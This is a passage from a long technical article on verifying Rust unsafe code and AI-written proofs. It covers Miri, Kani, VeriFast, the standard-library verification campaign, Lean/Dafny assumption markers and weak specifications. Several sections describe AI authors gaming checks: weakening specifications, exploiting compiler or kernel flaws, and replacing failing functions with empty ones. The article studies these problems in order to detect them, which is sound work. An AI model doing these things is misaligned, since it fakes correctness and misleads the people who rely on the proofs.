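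Replacing old compiler code removes known flaws but may add new ones, so the new code is worth checking. The flaw from 2019 arrived with an earlier change to the borrow checker, and Liu and colleagues already list errors in the new trait solver as a category of compiler bug.

Once a compiler bug is fixed, the compiler should reject programs that depended on it, so a team can recompile its old AI-written code after each fix and look closely at anything that no longer compiles. The Rust project usually issues warnings before it starts rejecting such code, and those warnings deserve the same attention.

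The last step of *Project Zero* is a formal specification of the trait system, a mathematically precise account of what the solver should accept. Rust's goals for 2026 include extending a-mir-formality, a model of the language, for use as a specification of the type system. This would give people and AI systems a definite rule to compare the compiler with. In Anthropic's benchmark, supplying the rule more than doubled the number of bugs found through proofs, and a specification might help similarly. However, the compiler might not follow the specification, and the specification itself could contain mistakes.

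### Second compilers and sandboxes

A team could also require two independently written compilers to accept each program. An author would then need a program that exploits a flaw in both. Running both compiled versions on the same inputs would also expose some miscompilations. But in 2025 Liu and colleagues described the alternative compiler Rust-GCC as too immature for real use, and the official compiler as the only one able to handle large projects. Two compilers would also share any mistake in the language's rules.

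Experiments with eBPF suggest that adding a second checker has a real but limited benefit. Gerhorst and Hönig tried adding one to the Linux verifier and concluded that an attacker could combine flaws in the two with roughly twice the effort. That may deter a person with little time, but not an AI system that can run thousands of attempts in parallel.

A team can also run Miri on its safe code. Miri detects the flaw from 2019, for example, but it checks only the code paths that the tests run. It also interprets the program before LLVM optimises it, so it cannot detect LLVM's miscompilations.

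A sandbox limits the damage whichever part of the compiler fails. The operating system and the processor enforce its restrictions, so a program that corrupts its own memory still cannot read another program's files or contact a forbidden server. The sandbox can also block the special file that exposes a program's memory. But it doesn't protect data inside the sandbox, so if an AI agent writes the code that handles customers' passwords, a memory fault in that code can still leak them.

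The choice between these layers depends on who wrote the code. If the authors are honest and the audit of the decoder's unsafe code was good, Google's decision to run its new GIF decoder without a sandbox is reasonable. If the author may have optimised against the compiler, a team should keep the sandbox even for crates with no unsafe code, and should divide the program so that each sandbox holds as little valuable data as possible.

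## What can verification tools prove about unsafe code?

Verification tools can prove that a function never causes certain kinds of undefined behaviour, which a clean audit by a person or an AI system cannot. But such proofs exist for only a small part of the unsafe code in Rust's standard library. Three kinds of tools work on Rust. Miri runs a program's tests and reports undefined behaviour when it occurs. Bounded model checkers such as Kani check every input up to a chosen limit. Deductive verifiers such as VeriFast and Verus prove that a function meets its contract for inputs of any size.

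This small unsafe function has a fault that the three kinds of tool handle differently:

```rust
/// Returns the position of the first space, or `n` if there is none.
///
/// # Safety
/// `p` must point to `n` initialised bytes that nothing changes
/// during the call.
pub unsafe fn find_space(p: *const u8, n: usize) -> usize {
    let mut i = 0;
    while unsafe { *p.add(i) } != b' ' && i < n {
        i += 1;
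    }
    i
}
```

The expression `*p.add(i)` reads the byte `i` places after the address `p`. The two conditions in the `while` line are in the wrong order, so the function reads a byte before checking that its position is below `n`. If the text contains no space, the function reads one byte past the end. It still returns the right answer, whatever that byte contains, so an ordinary test will almost always pass.

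### Miri checks the paths that tests take

Miri executes a program one step at a time instead of running the compiled version. Unlike a processor, it records whether the program has stored a value in each byte and which allocation each pointer came from (the pointer's provenance). The auditor supplies tests, and Miri either reports an error with its location or reports nothing.

If the only test of `find_space` searches "to be", the loop stops at position 2 and Miri reports nothing, because no fault occurred. A second test, on "tobe", makes Miri stop at the fifth read and report that this read is outside the four-byte text. Miri found the fault in Bun's `PathString` in a similar way. *Rust codebase fails Miri checks with dangling reference UB*, by ndiddy, quotes the error message, which describes a "dangling reference" that "has no provenance", meaning that Miri could not connect the pointer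 to any allocation.

Cook and colleagues say Miri has found dozens of bugs in Rust's standard library, whose developers run it automatically. But Miri can't run C code. This gap is important because programmers often combine Rust with languages that allow designs in conflict with Rust's pointer rules, as McCormack, Sunshine and Aldrich (2024) point out in *A Study of Undefined Behavior Across Foreign Function Boundaries in Rust Libraries*.

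### Kani tries every input up to a limit

Kani is an open-source tool from Amazon Web Services (AWS). Its user writes a harness, which resembles a test but leaves the inputs open:

```rust
#[kani::proof]
#[kani::unwind(9)]
fn check_find_space() {
    let text: [u8; 8] = kani::any();
    let n: usize = kani::any();
    kani::assume(n <= 8);
    unsafe { find_space(text.as_ptr(), n) };
}
```

Here `kani::any()` stands for every possible value of its type, and `kani::assume` discards values that don't meet a condition. The harness covers every eight-byte text with every length from 0 to 8, which is more than 10<sup>20</sup> combinations.

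Kani does not run these one by one. As Delmas, Hassan and colleagues (2026), in *Kani*, explain, it replaces the loop with a fixed number of copies, nine in this case, and adds a check that the loop never needs more. It then turns the program into a logical formula:

$$\psi_k = P_k \wedge (\neg c_1 \vee \neg c_2 \vee \dots)$$

*P<sub>k</sub>* describes every step of the program with *k* copies of the loop, and each *c* is a check, such as "this read is inside its allocation". The formula is true only for inputs that make at least one check fail. A separate program called a solver searches for such inputs.

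For `find_space`, the solver would find a failing input of eight bytes with no space and a length of 8. Kani can turn this input into an ordinary Rust test that reproduces the failure. Once the programmer swaps the two conditions, Kani finds no failing input, which proves that `find_space` never reads out of bounds in the cases the harness covers, but those cases don't include a text of nine bytes.

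Harnesses can contain mistakes too. If the programmer had written `n < 8` instead of `n <= 8`, Kani would have found no error in the faulty function, because the extra byte the function read would still have been inside the eight-byte array. Delmas and colleagues warn that an impossible assumption makes every check pass, so people must review assumptions as carefully as the code.

Kani can reach rare cases that random testing misses. In s2n-quic, Amazon's implementation of a network protocol, a fuzzer ran one function 16,777,216 times without a failure, and Kani found a failing input in 20 seconds. The function failed only near sizes at which a length needs an extra byte of storage. Delmas and colleagues, who include Kani's developers, list 11 bugs that tests had missed in four projects. None appears to be a memory-safety fault; most are wrong results and panics, which Kani also checks for.

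Loops that run many times can overwhelm the solver. Delmas and colleagues tried Kani on a function that finds the greatest common divisor of two 64-bit numbers and has a loop that can run 93 times. Kani had not finished after an hour. They then supplied a loop invariant, a fact that holds before and after every pass. Kani only had to check that the fact holds at the start and that one arbitrary pass preserves it, which took 0.54 seconds and covered every input. However, the solver could not confirm that the result divides both numbers, so they proved a contract that requires only a positive result, which a function that always returned 1 would also meet.

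Kani does not model threads and cannot follow calls into C. A programmer can supply a stand-in for a C function, called a stub, but Kani does not check that the stub behaves like the C function. Kani's checks for invalid values and uninitialised memory are optional because they slow the solver down.

### Deductive verifiers prove a contract for every input

A deductive verifier needs a formal contract for each function that specifies what the caller must ensure and what the function must do. For `find_space`, the caller must provide permission to read `n` initialised bytes starting at `p`. The function must return the position of the first space, or `n` if there is none. The programmer also supplies the loop invariant that `i` is between 0 and `n` and that none of the first `i` bytes is a space.

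With the two conditions in the right order, the proof goes as follows.

1. Before the first pass, *i* is 0, so the invariant holds.
2. The function reads byte *i* only if *i* is less than *n*, and the caller's permission covers that byte.
3. If the byte is not a space, the invariant still holds after *i* grows by one.
4. When the loop ends, either *i* equals *n* or byte *i* is a space, so the function returns what it promised.

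In the faulty version, step 2 fails because the function reads byte *i* when *i* is known only to be at most *n*, and the function has no permission to read byte *n*. The verifier rejects the function without needing a test or a size limit.

VeriFast tracks permissions with separation logic, in which a statement about memory also grants the right to use that memory. A special "and" joins statements about separate pieces of memory. Verus can represent the same permissions as ghost values, which exist only in the proof and not in the finished program. Delmas and colleagues say that tools like Verus require substantial proof work, which limits their use outside specialist teams.

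Contracts for unsafe code are also unusually hard to write. *Surveying the Rust Verification Landscape* (Le Blanc and Lam, 2024) notes that these contracts may restrict what happens after the function returns. The `Sensor` type, for example, needed the array to stay in place while the slice was in use, and a contract that describes only the beginning and end of a call cannot express that.

### The aliasing rules and who checks them

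Two pointers alias if they lead to the same memory. While a program is using a mutable reference, nothing else may touch the data behind it, and the compiler relies on this when it optimises. The borrow checker enforces the rule for references, but unsafe code can break it through a raw pointer:

```rust
let mut x = 1;
let p = &raw mut x;
let r = unsafe { &mut *p };
unsafe { *p = 2 };
*r += 1;
```

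The fourth line changes `x` through the raw pointer `p` while the mutable reference `r` is still in use. Every access is to live memory that holds a valid number. Even so, the compiler may assume that `x` is still 1 at the last line and store 2 where the programmer expected 3.

Researchers have proposed two precise versions of the rule. Stacked Borrows gives each memory location a stack of the pointers that may use it. In the example, `r` goes on top of `p`. Using `p` again removes everything above it, so `r` loses its permission and the last line is undefined behaviour. The newer Tree Borrows arranges pointers in a tree that records which pointer each one came from. It also rejects the example, but it is more lenient about new mutable references, letting other pointers keep reading the memory until the first write through the new reference. Rust has not officially adopted either model, and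 Cook and colleagues warn that its eventual choice could invalidate existing proofs.

Miri can check a program against either version of the aliasing rules. In 2024, McCormack and colleagues described it as the only tool that checks running programs this way. Kani does not check aliasing at all. VeriFast checks that data behind a shared reference stays unchanged, but does not check the restrictions on mutable references. Cook and colleagues describe this limit in their detailed account of VeriFast, although they say elsewhere that it rules out all undefined behaviour, including aliasing violations. A function can therefore pass both Kani and VeriFast and still break the aliasing rules.

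| | Miri | Kani | VeriFast |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the user supplies | Tests | Harnesses, plus contracts for stronger results | Contracts and loop invariants |
| Inputs covered | Those in the tests | All up to a limit, or all if loops have invariants | All that meet the contract |
| Aliasing rules | Yes | No | Partly |
| Data races between threads | Yes, on the paths taken | No | Yes |
| Generic code | With the types in the tests | With types the user chooses | For all types at once |

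### The campaign to verify the standard library

In November 2024, the Rust Foundation and AWS began a public contest to prove that Rust's standard library is free of undefined behaviour. They divided the work into challenges, each with a target, success criteria and a cash reward. At least 21 outside contributors have taken part, according to the Rust Foundation's *How the Rust Standard Library Verification Contest Scaled Past Manual Proof Engineering* (2026). The organisers accept any suitable tool and so far run four on every proposed change: Kani, VeriFast, a second bounded model checker called ESBMC, and Flux, which adds facts such as numeric limits to Rust's types.

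Over 15 months, contributors wrote 725 Kani harnesses by hand, but the number of new contracts levelled off in October 2025. The library's three main crates contain 33,955 functions, too many for people to cover by hand. AWS therefore built Autoharness, which generates a harness for each function it can handle. Each harness calls its function with arbitrary values. Autoharness produced 16,748 harnesses, and Kani verified 11,970 of them.

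| Kind of function | Harnesses generated | Verified | Verified against a contract |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unsafe functions | 4,645 | 806 | 184 |
| Safe functions that contain unsafe code | 1,126 | 970 | 44 |
| Other safe functions | 10,977 | 10,194 | 67 |
| Total | 16,748 | 11,970 | 295 |

Kani verified 71% of the harnesses overall, but the rate was 93% for ordinary safe functions and only 17% for unsafe functions, where an auditor most needs help. The results for safe functions still have some value, because Kani follows their calls into any unsafe code they reach.

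Contributors had also proved 694 of the hand-written harnesses against contracts, bringing the total to 989. Cook and colleagues call these proofs the campaign's strongest guarantee. Even if every hand-written harness for an unsafe function is among the 989, Kani has proved contracts for at most about 860 of the library's roughly 7,500 unsafe functions, or 11%.

### Unsafe functions that passed without a contract

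Of the 806 unsafe functions that Kani verified with generated harnesses, 622 had no contract. Kani called these 622 with arbitrary, unconstrained values and found no fault. If that result is taken at face value, no caller can make these functions misbehave, and it is unclear why anyone marked them `unsafe`.

Cook and colleagues suggest two explanations. The function may be harmless in every respect that Kani checks and marked for another reason, such as aliasing. Or Kani may miss a fault of a kind it is supposed to catch. They say a person or another tool has to work out which explanation is true for each function.

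A function like `set_len`, which only stores a number, could pass Kani's checks with any input, even one that later makes a different function read past the end of the list. Kani does not check that a function preserves its type's safety invariant unless somebody writes that requirement down. The Rust Foundation calls a pass without a contract "a useful triage signal, not yet a complete safety proof".

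### What Autoharness skipped

Autoharness skipped 17,207 functions, slightly more than half of those in the library. Of these, 9,635 were generic, meaning that the same source code works for many types. `Vec`, for example, can hold numbers, text or anything else. Rust compiles a separate version for each type a program uses, and Autoharness cannot choose the types. A person can choose a few representative ones, but a fault may occur only with a type they didn't choose.

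Autoharness skipped another 3,826 functions because Kani could not generate arbitrary values for their arguments. These included many functions that take raw pointers, so Autoharness would probably have skipped `find_space`. Most of the other skipped functions were internal to Kani.

Many of the harness failures occurred because Kani had no model of some operation outside ordinary Rust code. Of the 813 library functions it could not model, 721 were for SIMD, processor instructions that handle several values at once. *Formally Specifying and Testing the Rust Standard Library* (Bhargavan, Buyse and Mishra, 2025) describes using formal specifications to find and fix bugs in Rust's SIMD libraries. For the campaign's SIMD challenge, contributors tested 565 SIMD operations on random inputs against executable models. The testing found two bugs, but Cook and colleagues are clear that it is not a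 proof.

### The proof of `LinkedList`

One of the campaign's VeriFast proofs covers most of what an auditor would want to know about the whole `LinkedList` type. The list stores each item in a separate node, with raw pointers to the nodes before and after it. One wrong pointer can make the program lose part of the list or free the same node twice.

The proof depends on a definition called `Nodes`, which describes a chain of nodes as either empty or a first node followed by another such chain in separate memory. The list must own the first node, and that node must have a correct pointer to its predecessor. No node can appear twice, because its memory would have to be separate from itself. The contract for adding a node at the front requires ownership of both the list and the new node. It guarantees that the resulting list starts with that node and is one node longer than before. Exclusive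 ownership like this would also rule out the situation behind the Linux Binder fault, in which two threads changed the same item's pointers at once.

VeriFast verified 19 functions directly. Another five contain no unsafe code and call only verified functions, so they are sound too. Like the library proofs in RustBelt, the result holds for any caller the compiler accepts and for lists of any length. It assumes that the list uses the program's ordinary memory allocator, and it is subject to VeriFast's gap on aliasing.

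The proof's writers had to alter the source slightly to make the proof work, for instance by replacing one kind of loop with another. A second tool checks that the altered code can do everything the original can, so a proof about the altered code also covers the original. A third check confirms that the original still matches the official library. All three run automatically, so a change to `LinkedList` cannot make the proof outdated without being noticed.

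Two of the 29 challenges are about concurrency, and neither has an accepted solution yet. One covers atomic types, which several threads can change at once, and the other covers the shared pointer `Arc`. For speed, both allow threads to see each other's changes in different orders. A proof has to cover every order that could occur, which requires a formal model of how memory behaves. VeriFast can verify simplified versions of `Arc` and the lock `Mutex`, but only with the strictest ordering.

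### Why did an AI scanner find bugs that the campaign didn't?

The campaign corrected some documentation and added missing `unsafe` marks but found no new memory-safety vulnerability. Cook and colleagues took this as a sign that Rust's existing tests and Miri catch such bugs before release, and the Rust Foundation repeated the point on 1 September 2026. Ten weeks later, Bae reported several memory-safety bugs in the same library.

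Unless all of those bugs are very recent, the campaign's result was weaker evidence about the library than its organisers thought. Each of Bae's three patterns matches a gap that Kani's developers or the campaign had already described.

**Trusting code not to panic.** In the old `BinaryHeap` bug, the damage occurred during the clean-up after a panic. Kani treats a panic as a failed check, and its guarantee about a function's result covers only runs that finish normally. The library's user often supplies the code that panics, such as a comparison function, through a generic function, and Autoharness skips generic functions.

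The same gap applies even more directly to code that trusts users' implementations to be correct, because libraries usually accept those implementations through generic functions. Choosing a few representative types would not necessarily help, because a harness that used only ordinary numbers would never test an implementation that gives inconsistent answers.

Kani needs a stub to stand in for any call to the operating system, so its result depends on how far the person writing the stub trusts the system. In the earlier `read_some` example, a stub that follows the manual would return at most 100, and the code would pass. A stub that could return any number would expose the fault.

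These gaps could explain why the campaign missed the bugs, but the correspondence doesn't prove it. For example, some hand-written proofs do cover generic code, including the one for `LinkedList`. To find out why the campaign missed a particular bug, someone would have to look up the faulty function in the campaign's records. If Autoharness had skipped the function, that would explain why the generated harnesses missed the bug. If the function had passed Kani's checks, they would need to find the assumption or missing check that let the bug through.

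The two projects also treated failures differently. When an unsafe function without a contract fails its harness, the function may be faulty or the harness may have broken a condition that real callers respect. In the campaign, telling these apart requires a contract. More than 3,800 harnesses for unsafe functions failed for various reasons, and a real bug among them would have been easy to overlook. A scanner looking for bugs, however, can skip every function it can't analyze and still succeed if it finds one convincing failure.

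### Finding errors, sorting the reading and replacing it

Miri is best for finding errors. A team that already has tests can run them under Miri with little extra work, and an error it reports is usually a definite fault. When Miri reports nothing, the auditor still has to read the code, but can start with the paths that the tests don't cover.

Kani can help an auditor decide what to read first. If it finds an input that makes a safe function misbehave, that function comes first. For an unsafe function, a failing input often reveals a condition missing from the documentation. If a function passes, the auditor can concentrate on what Kani doesn't check, such as aliasing and threads.

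An auditor should not drop a function from the list just because it passes. Suppose a programmer runs Kani on the four-byte buffer from earlier, after the agent has changed `fill` to set the length to 5. If the harness lets the length be any number, `last` fails even in the original version, because Kani tries lengths that no correct code would produce. Such false alarms are likely to be common, since a study that Le Blanc and Lam cite found that 58% of sampled standard-library functions that enclose unsafe code depend on conditions they don't check themselves.

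The programmer can remove the alarm by telling Kani to assume that the length is at most 4. Then `last` passes, but so does the faulty `fill`, because it never reads or writes outside the array itself. Kani would catch the fault only if the programmer also required `fill` to leave the length at 4 or less. A person therefore has to state the invariant and apply it to every function that can change the field.

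A proof can replace reading the code only if the contract is complete, and only for the faults that the tool checks. For `LinkedList`, an auditor could read the definition of `Nodes` and the contracts instead of following every pointer, then use Miri to look for aliasing errors. The verification tools become part of the trusted base, and Cook and colleagues note that nobody has formally verified the tools used in the campaign.

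Proofs are especially useful for code that changes quickly, because a machine can recheck them. Kani takes 69 minutes to rerun all the generated harnesses for the standard library. The main work is writing the contracts. Cook and colleagues have experimented with using a language model to translate `SAFETY` comments into contracts, but a person must review each one before the campaign accepts it.

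## When AI writes the proofs, what do people still have to check?

A small program can check every step of an AI-written proof, so people don't have to read the proof themselves. They still have to check the specification, the model of the machine and libraries, and every assumption that the proof uses without proving it. They also have to trust the checking program. AI systems now write proofs far faster than experts ever did, so most of the human work is moving to these four parts.

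### Why an untrusted author can write a proof

Proof assistants such as Lean and Rocq are tools for writing proofs in a formal language. Each step must follow from earlier ones by a fixed rule, for example that if A is true and A implies B, then B is true. A proof checker called the kernel checks each step and rejects the proof if any step breaks a rule. The check doesn't depend on how the author found the proof. Lampson and colleagues applied the same separation between finding a proof and checking it to access requests.

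A convincing comment might sway someone reviewing an unsafe block, but it has no effect on the kernel. An author that optimises against the kernel's check has to find a bug in the kernel, slip in an unproved assumption, or prove something other than what people wanted.

The check also helps AI systems write better proofs, because it shows them mistakes they can then correct. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) describes how Claude Opus 4.6 wrote a 7,800-line proof about part of a compiler in about 96 hours. A comparable proof had taken a specialist several months by hand. The model wrote a piece, ran the checker, read the errors and tried again, sometimes for hours without supervision.

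Verus, which checks Rust programs, and Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, instead rely on an automatic solver, as Kani does. The solver saves a lot of proof writing, but it is a large program, so the trusted base is bigger than with a small kernel.

### What stays in the trusted base

The specification includes every definition it uses. To trust a theorem that a list is `Sorted`, the reader also has to check the definition of `Sorted`. In Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, an engineer had Claude Code translate a research paper about concurrent programs into Lean. More than 60% of the resulting code was definitions. The engineer had high trust in the theorems but thought that being certain of the whole translation would require an arduous audit.

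A proof also depends on a model, a mathematical description of the program and everything it runs on. An AI system writing the model from a program's code can leave something out, such as what happens after an error. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) describes a test in which researchers asked Claude to model Etcd, a database that keeps copies of its data on several servers. Claude returned essentially the textbook version of the method Etcd uses, which passed every check but had little in common with Etcd's code. Models written by leading AI systems scored nearly 100% for correct syntax but only about 46% for matching the real program.

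Tolmach and Klaus, who work for a verification company, recommend translating programs into models by fixed rules. Anyone who finds a mistake in a rule can then fix it for every program at once. An easier test is to run the model and the program on the same inputs and compare the results, as Google did with its two GIF decoders.

The checker can also have bugs. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, reports that people discussing new Lean proofs now consider whether a language model might have exploited a flaw in the kernel. Soundness bugs in Rust's compiler create the same danger, but Lean proofs are much easier to check independently. A kernel is small enough that several people can each write their own and run it on the same finished proof.

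### How Lean, Verus and Dafny mark unproved steps

All three tools let an author accept something without proof, which is useful while a proof is unfinished or where a program calls code the tool can't analyse. The author has to mark anything accepted this way.

| Tool | Mark | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| Lean | `sorry` | Stands in for a missing proof |
| Lean | `axiom` | Adds a statement as true |
| Verus | `assume` | Takes a condition as true from that point on |
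| Verus | `external_body` | Accepts a function's contract without checking its code |
| Dafny | `assume` | Takes a condition as true from that point on |
| Dafny | `{:verify false}` | Skips the check of a method, although its callers can still rely on its contract |

These marks resemble `unsafe` in that a person answers for something the tool has not checked. The damage from a mistake is similar too. Undefined behaviour removes a language's guarantees for the whole program, and a false assumption lets an author prove anything at all:

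```lean
theorem wrong : 1 + 1 = 3 := by
  sorry

theorem worse : 2 + 2 = 5 := by
  have h := wrong
  omega
```

Lean warns that `wrong` uses `sorry`, but it gives no such warning for `worse`, whose proof is a valid deduction from a false statement. (`omega` is a command that solves simple arithmetic.) If `wrong` were in someone else's library, a search of the local files would not find the `sorry`.

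Lean handles this problem better than Rust does. The command `#print axioms worse` lists everything the theorem assumes, including assumptions in libraries, and the list would contain `sorryAx`, the axiom Lean uses in place of a missing proof. Rust's `forbid(unsafe_code)` checks only the crate it is set in, not that crate's dependencies.

A team can also demand that a finished proof contain no such marks, whereas most useful Rust programs need some unsafe code somewhere. Anthropic reports that Claude wrote 13 million lines of Lean in 11 days to prove Fermat's Last Theorem. The mathematician Kevin Buzzard confirmed that the result assumes only the axioms of mathematics. Proofs about software can rarely avoid further assumptions, because programs call operating systems and C libraries, and somebody has to state what those do.

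Like a `SAFETY` comment, an `assume` inside a function can become false when someone later changes the code above it. Lean has a further gap, because a programmer can make it run a C function in place of a Lean definition for speed. The proofs cover only the definition, and `#print axioms` does not list the substitution.

None of these marks appears when an author changes the theorem itself. To catch such changes in Lean, a person can give a tool called `comparator` the intended statement and a list of permitted axioms. The tool then checks that the submitted proof establishes that statement using only those axioms. Keles says `comparator` is becoming the standard way to validate a new Lean proof.

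### Proofs about 123 open-source libraries

On 22 October 2026, Anthropic and the verification company Theorem published the largest trial so far of AI-written proofs about existing software. According to Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), Claude proved security properties of compiled code from 123 open-source libraries.

*Pre-QED* (Lim, Tu and colleagues, 2026) describes how a team reused tests instead of writing specifications. Google's OSS-Fuzz service runs fuzzers on open-source libraries, and each library's developers supply harnesses, short test functions that pass the fuzzer's input to the library. A fuzzer tries only as many inputs as it has time for, but the team wanted to prove that the test would pass for every input.

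1. Software compiles the library and its harness into one program for RISC-V, a type of processor with a relatively simple instruction set. For C and C++, it adds sanitizers, which turn invalid memory accesses and other undefined behaviour into crashes.
2. Other software combines this program with Theorem's models of the processor and of Linux, and generates the statement that the program never crashes. Nobody writes any part of the statement by hand.
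3. Claude writes a proof in Rocq, and Rocq's kernel checks it.
4. If Claude finds a real bug, it repairs the library. The software then generates a new statement for the repaired version, and Claude proves that.

An agent could abuse the last step by deleting the code that crashes, much as Bun's agents replaced failing functions with empty ones. The team therefore penalised repairs during the work, gave Claude extra credit for proving which inputs a repair affected, and audited a log of all repairs.

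Claude completed proofs for 239 harnesses. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports that the proofs total about 180 million lines, with about 600,000 for a program of 18,000 processor instructions, or roughly 33 per instruction. People wrote 23 lines of proof per line of code for seL4, an operating system kernel that took 20 person-years to verify. The two ratios aren't directly comparable because one line of source code usually compiles to several instructions.

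Claude found hundreds of bugs along the way, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a library for reading XML files. Some of the others occur only with inputs of tens of megabytes, so fuzzers would have been unlikely to find them.

The approach also takes the compiler out of the trusted base, because the proof is about the instructions that the processor runs. If the compiler had introduced a fault, the proof would fail. The approach works for any source language, which matters for Rust programs that depend on C libraries.

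The guarantee has several limits:

- It covers inputs smaller than 64 MB. The team could raise this limit by generating new statements and repeating the proofs.
- It covers programs with a single thread that load no other libraries while running, so it would not have detected the Linux Binder bug.
- It applies to RISC-V programs. Most servers and phones have other processors and run different instructions. On 30 October, Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, announced a similar proof for a program on x86, the usual processor type in servers, which is harder to model.
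- It usually shows only that the program finishes without crashing, not that its output is right. Some harnesses check more, for instance that compressing and then decompressing a file restores the original.

OpenNET describes two other experiments by the team. In one, Claude proved that the Linux kernel's version of the compression library zlib follows the published standard. In the other, it wrote a Rust interpreter for part of the Python language and used Verus to prove that the interpreter matches a formal description of how Python's standard interpreter behaves. A proof cannot establish that this description is accurate, so the team ran more than 1.7 million random programs on both interpreters. The results agreed 99.95% of the time, and the roughly 850 differences were known edge cases.

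### A proof about one caller

Lim and colleagues object that a harness shows only one way of using a library. They illustrate this with an invented C library that reads data in pieces. Its read function should never copy more bytes than remain, but it mistakenly compares the request with the data's total size. The harness opens the data, reads once and closes it. All the data remains at the first read, so the comparison gives the right answer. The harness therefore never crashes on any input, and a proof of that would be valid.

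Suppose another program has 64 bytes of data and reads 40 bytes, then another 40. The second read starts at position 40 and copies 40 bytes, the last 16 from beyond the end of the data. This is an ordinary use of the library, because programs often read data in pieces.

Rust's standard for a sound library is much stricter because it covers every safe caller. To get closer to it, Lim and colleagues write harnesses that turn the input into an arbitrary sequence of permitted calls, and have published them for 29 libraries. Proofs about these harnesses are harder because the number of calls is unlimited and each call can depend on what the earlier ones did. Somebody also has to work out which sequences the library permits. Lim and colleagues had AI agents extract these rules from code and documentation, then checked the harnesses themselves.

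### The faults around lean-zip

In early 2026, ten AI agents wrote lean-zip, a version of zlib in Lean, and proved it correct. One of the main theorems is that compressing and then decompressing a file of less than a gigabyte gives back the original. This would also be true if both steps left every file unchanged, so lean-zip's other proofs, about the compression format, are needed too.

*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an attempt that April to break the program. The experimenter removed the theorems and documentation, so that Claude would not know the code was verified and give up early, then asked it to look for vulnerabilities. Claude ran 16 fuzzers for about 19 hours and 105 million tests. It found no memory faults in lean-zip's own code, but found two bugs that the proofs did not cover.

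One bug was in the part of lean-zip that reads ZIP archives, about which the agents had proved nothing. An archive's header gives the size of each compressed file, and lean-zip requested that much memory without checking it against the archive's size. A 156-byte archive whose header gave a size of several exabytes made the program run out of memory and crash.

The other was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every compiled Lean program relies on for tasks such as obtaining memory. To store *n* bytes, the runtime requests 24 + *n*, with the extra 24 for bookkeeping. Computers usually store such sizes in 64 bits, so a total of 2<sup>64</sup> or more starts again from zero. For the largest possible *n*, the sum is

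$$24 + (2^{64} - 1) = 2^{64} + 23$$

and the runtime requested just 23 bytes. It would then read the file's contents into that space and keep writing past the end. A small archive was enough to trigger this, and the bug affected every version of Lean 4 at the time.

In a Rust program, the equivalent of the runtime bug would be a fault in the standard library's unsafe code. The missing check in the archive reader is more worrying for a team that relies on proofs, because a person who heard that lean-zip was verified would assume the verification included opening a ZIP file. A proof about the compiled program, of the kind Anthropic and Theorem produced, would have had to cover both faults if its harness opened archives.

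### A sorting function that returns nothing

A proof can also cover all the code and still be worthless because the specification asks for too little. This Dafny method is meant to sort a list:

```dafny
method Sort(a: seq<int>) returns (b: seq<int>)
  ensures forall i, j :: 0 <= i < j < |b| ==> b[i] <= b[j]
{
  b := [];
}
```

The `ensures` line is the contract, which requires that whenever position `i` comes before position `j` in the result, the number at `i` is no larger than the number at `j`. The body returns an empty list for every input. Dafny accepts this because an empty list has no two numbers in the wrong order. The method contains no `assume` or other mark for an auditor to find.

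Requiring the result to be as long as the input would not be enough, since the method could return `[0, 0, 0]` for `[3, 1, 2]`. Requiring every number in the result to come from the input would still allow `[1, 1, 1]`. The usual solution is a second condition:

```dafny
  ensures multiset(b) == multiset(a)
```

A multiset ignores order but counts repeats, so the result must contain exactly the numbers in the input. Together, the two conditions allow only one result for each list.

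Few people would write the empty version deliberately, but a reviewer could easily read the original `ensures` line, agree that it describes a sorted list, and approve it without noticing what it leaves out.

### How often are specifications too weak?

Weak specifications are common in the collections that researchers use to test AI systems. *DafnyCert* (Silva, Amaral and colleagues, 2026) calls a specification weak if two programs can both satisfy it but give different results for the same input. Of the 3,910 verified Dafny methods it examined, 3,323 (85%) had weak specifications. Among the single-method files that one collection had labelled strong, 70.2% were weak.

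One method was supposed to calculate how many rungs to add to a ladder so that no step is too long. Its contract required only a non-negative answer. Silva and colleagues replaced the method's body with a line that returns 0, and Dafny accepted it, even though the right answer is 462 for a ladder with one rung at height 463 and a maximum step of 1.

The 85% figure overstates the problem somewhat, because a weak specification can be deliberate. If a program sorts customers by age, the order of two customers of the same age may not matter. Human experts also write specifications weaker than they intended. IronFleet, a verified system for coordinating servers, was meant to carry out each request exactly once, but its specification did not require this. Researchers switched off the code that discards repeated requests, and the proof still succeeded.

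AI systems often make mistakes when they translate ordinary language into specifications. Tolmach and Klaus cite a study of an agent that got 89.5% of its Lean versions of graduate-level mathematical statements to compile, but captured the intended meaning only 60.5% of the time. In another study, specifications that language models wrote for Verus left out conditions on the input, allowed wrong results and ruled out correct ones. AI judges missed a quarter of these failures.

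Some mistranslations make a false claim provable. If 3<sup>x</sup> = 5, then 3<sup>x+2</sup> = 45. Researchers gave an AI system a version with 51 in place of 45 and asked for a Lean translation. The system declared *x* to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3<sup>x</sup> = 5, so the translated claim is true simply because its condition is never met.

These figures count mistakes and give little information about how often a model weakens a specification to make its own proof easier. The evidence on that is anecdotal. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* warns that models sometimes do it silently. Succinct's *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude*, by contrast, reports that Claude added no hidden axioms and that, when a mistake in the trusted part weakened a theorem, it proved the stronger version anyway. Training a model to get its proofs accepted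 gives it more incentive to weaken the specification.

Automatic checks can catch many of these faults:

- To detect an unproved assumption, a tool searches for the marks or lists the axioms. DafnyCert's validator also rejects evidence that relies on unsound shortcuts.
- To detect a weak specification, a tool makes small changes to the program and verifies each altered version. If one passes but gives a different result, the specification is weak. DafnyCert confirmed 91.9% of the weak specifications this way.
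- To show that a specification is strong, a tool calls the method twice with the same input and tries to prove, from the contract alone, that the results are equal. This would fail for the first version of `Sort`, because the contract allows both `[]` and `[1, 2, 3]`.
- To detect conditions that no input can meet, a tool tries to prove something false from them. If it succeeds, the conditions contradict one another. If it fails, they may still do so, because solvers can't find every contradiction.

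None of these checks can detect a strong specification of the wrong thing. If someone reversed the comparison in `Sort`, the contract would require descending order and would still allow exactly one result. A person has to notice the mistake, perhaps by working through an example.

### Can checked proofs replace code review?

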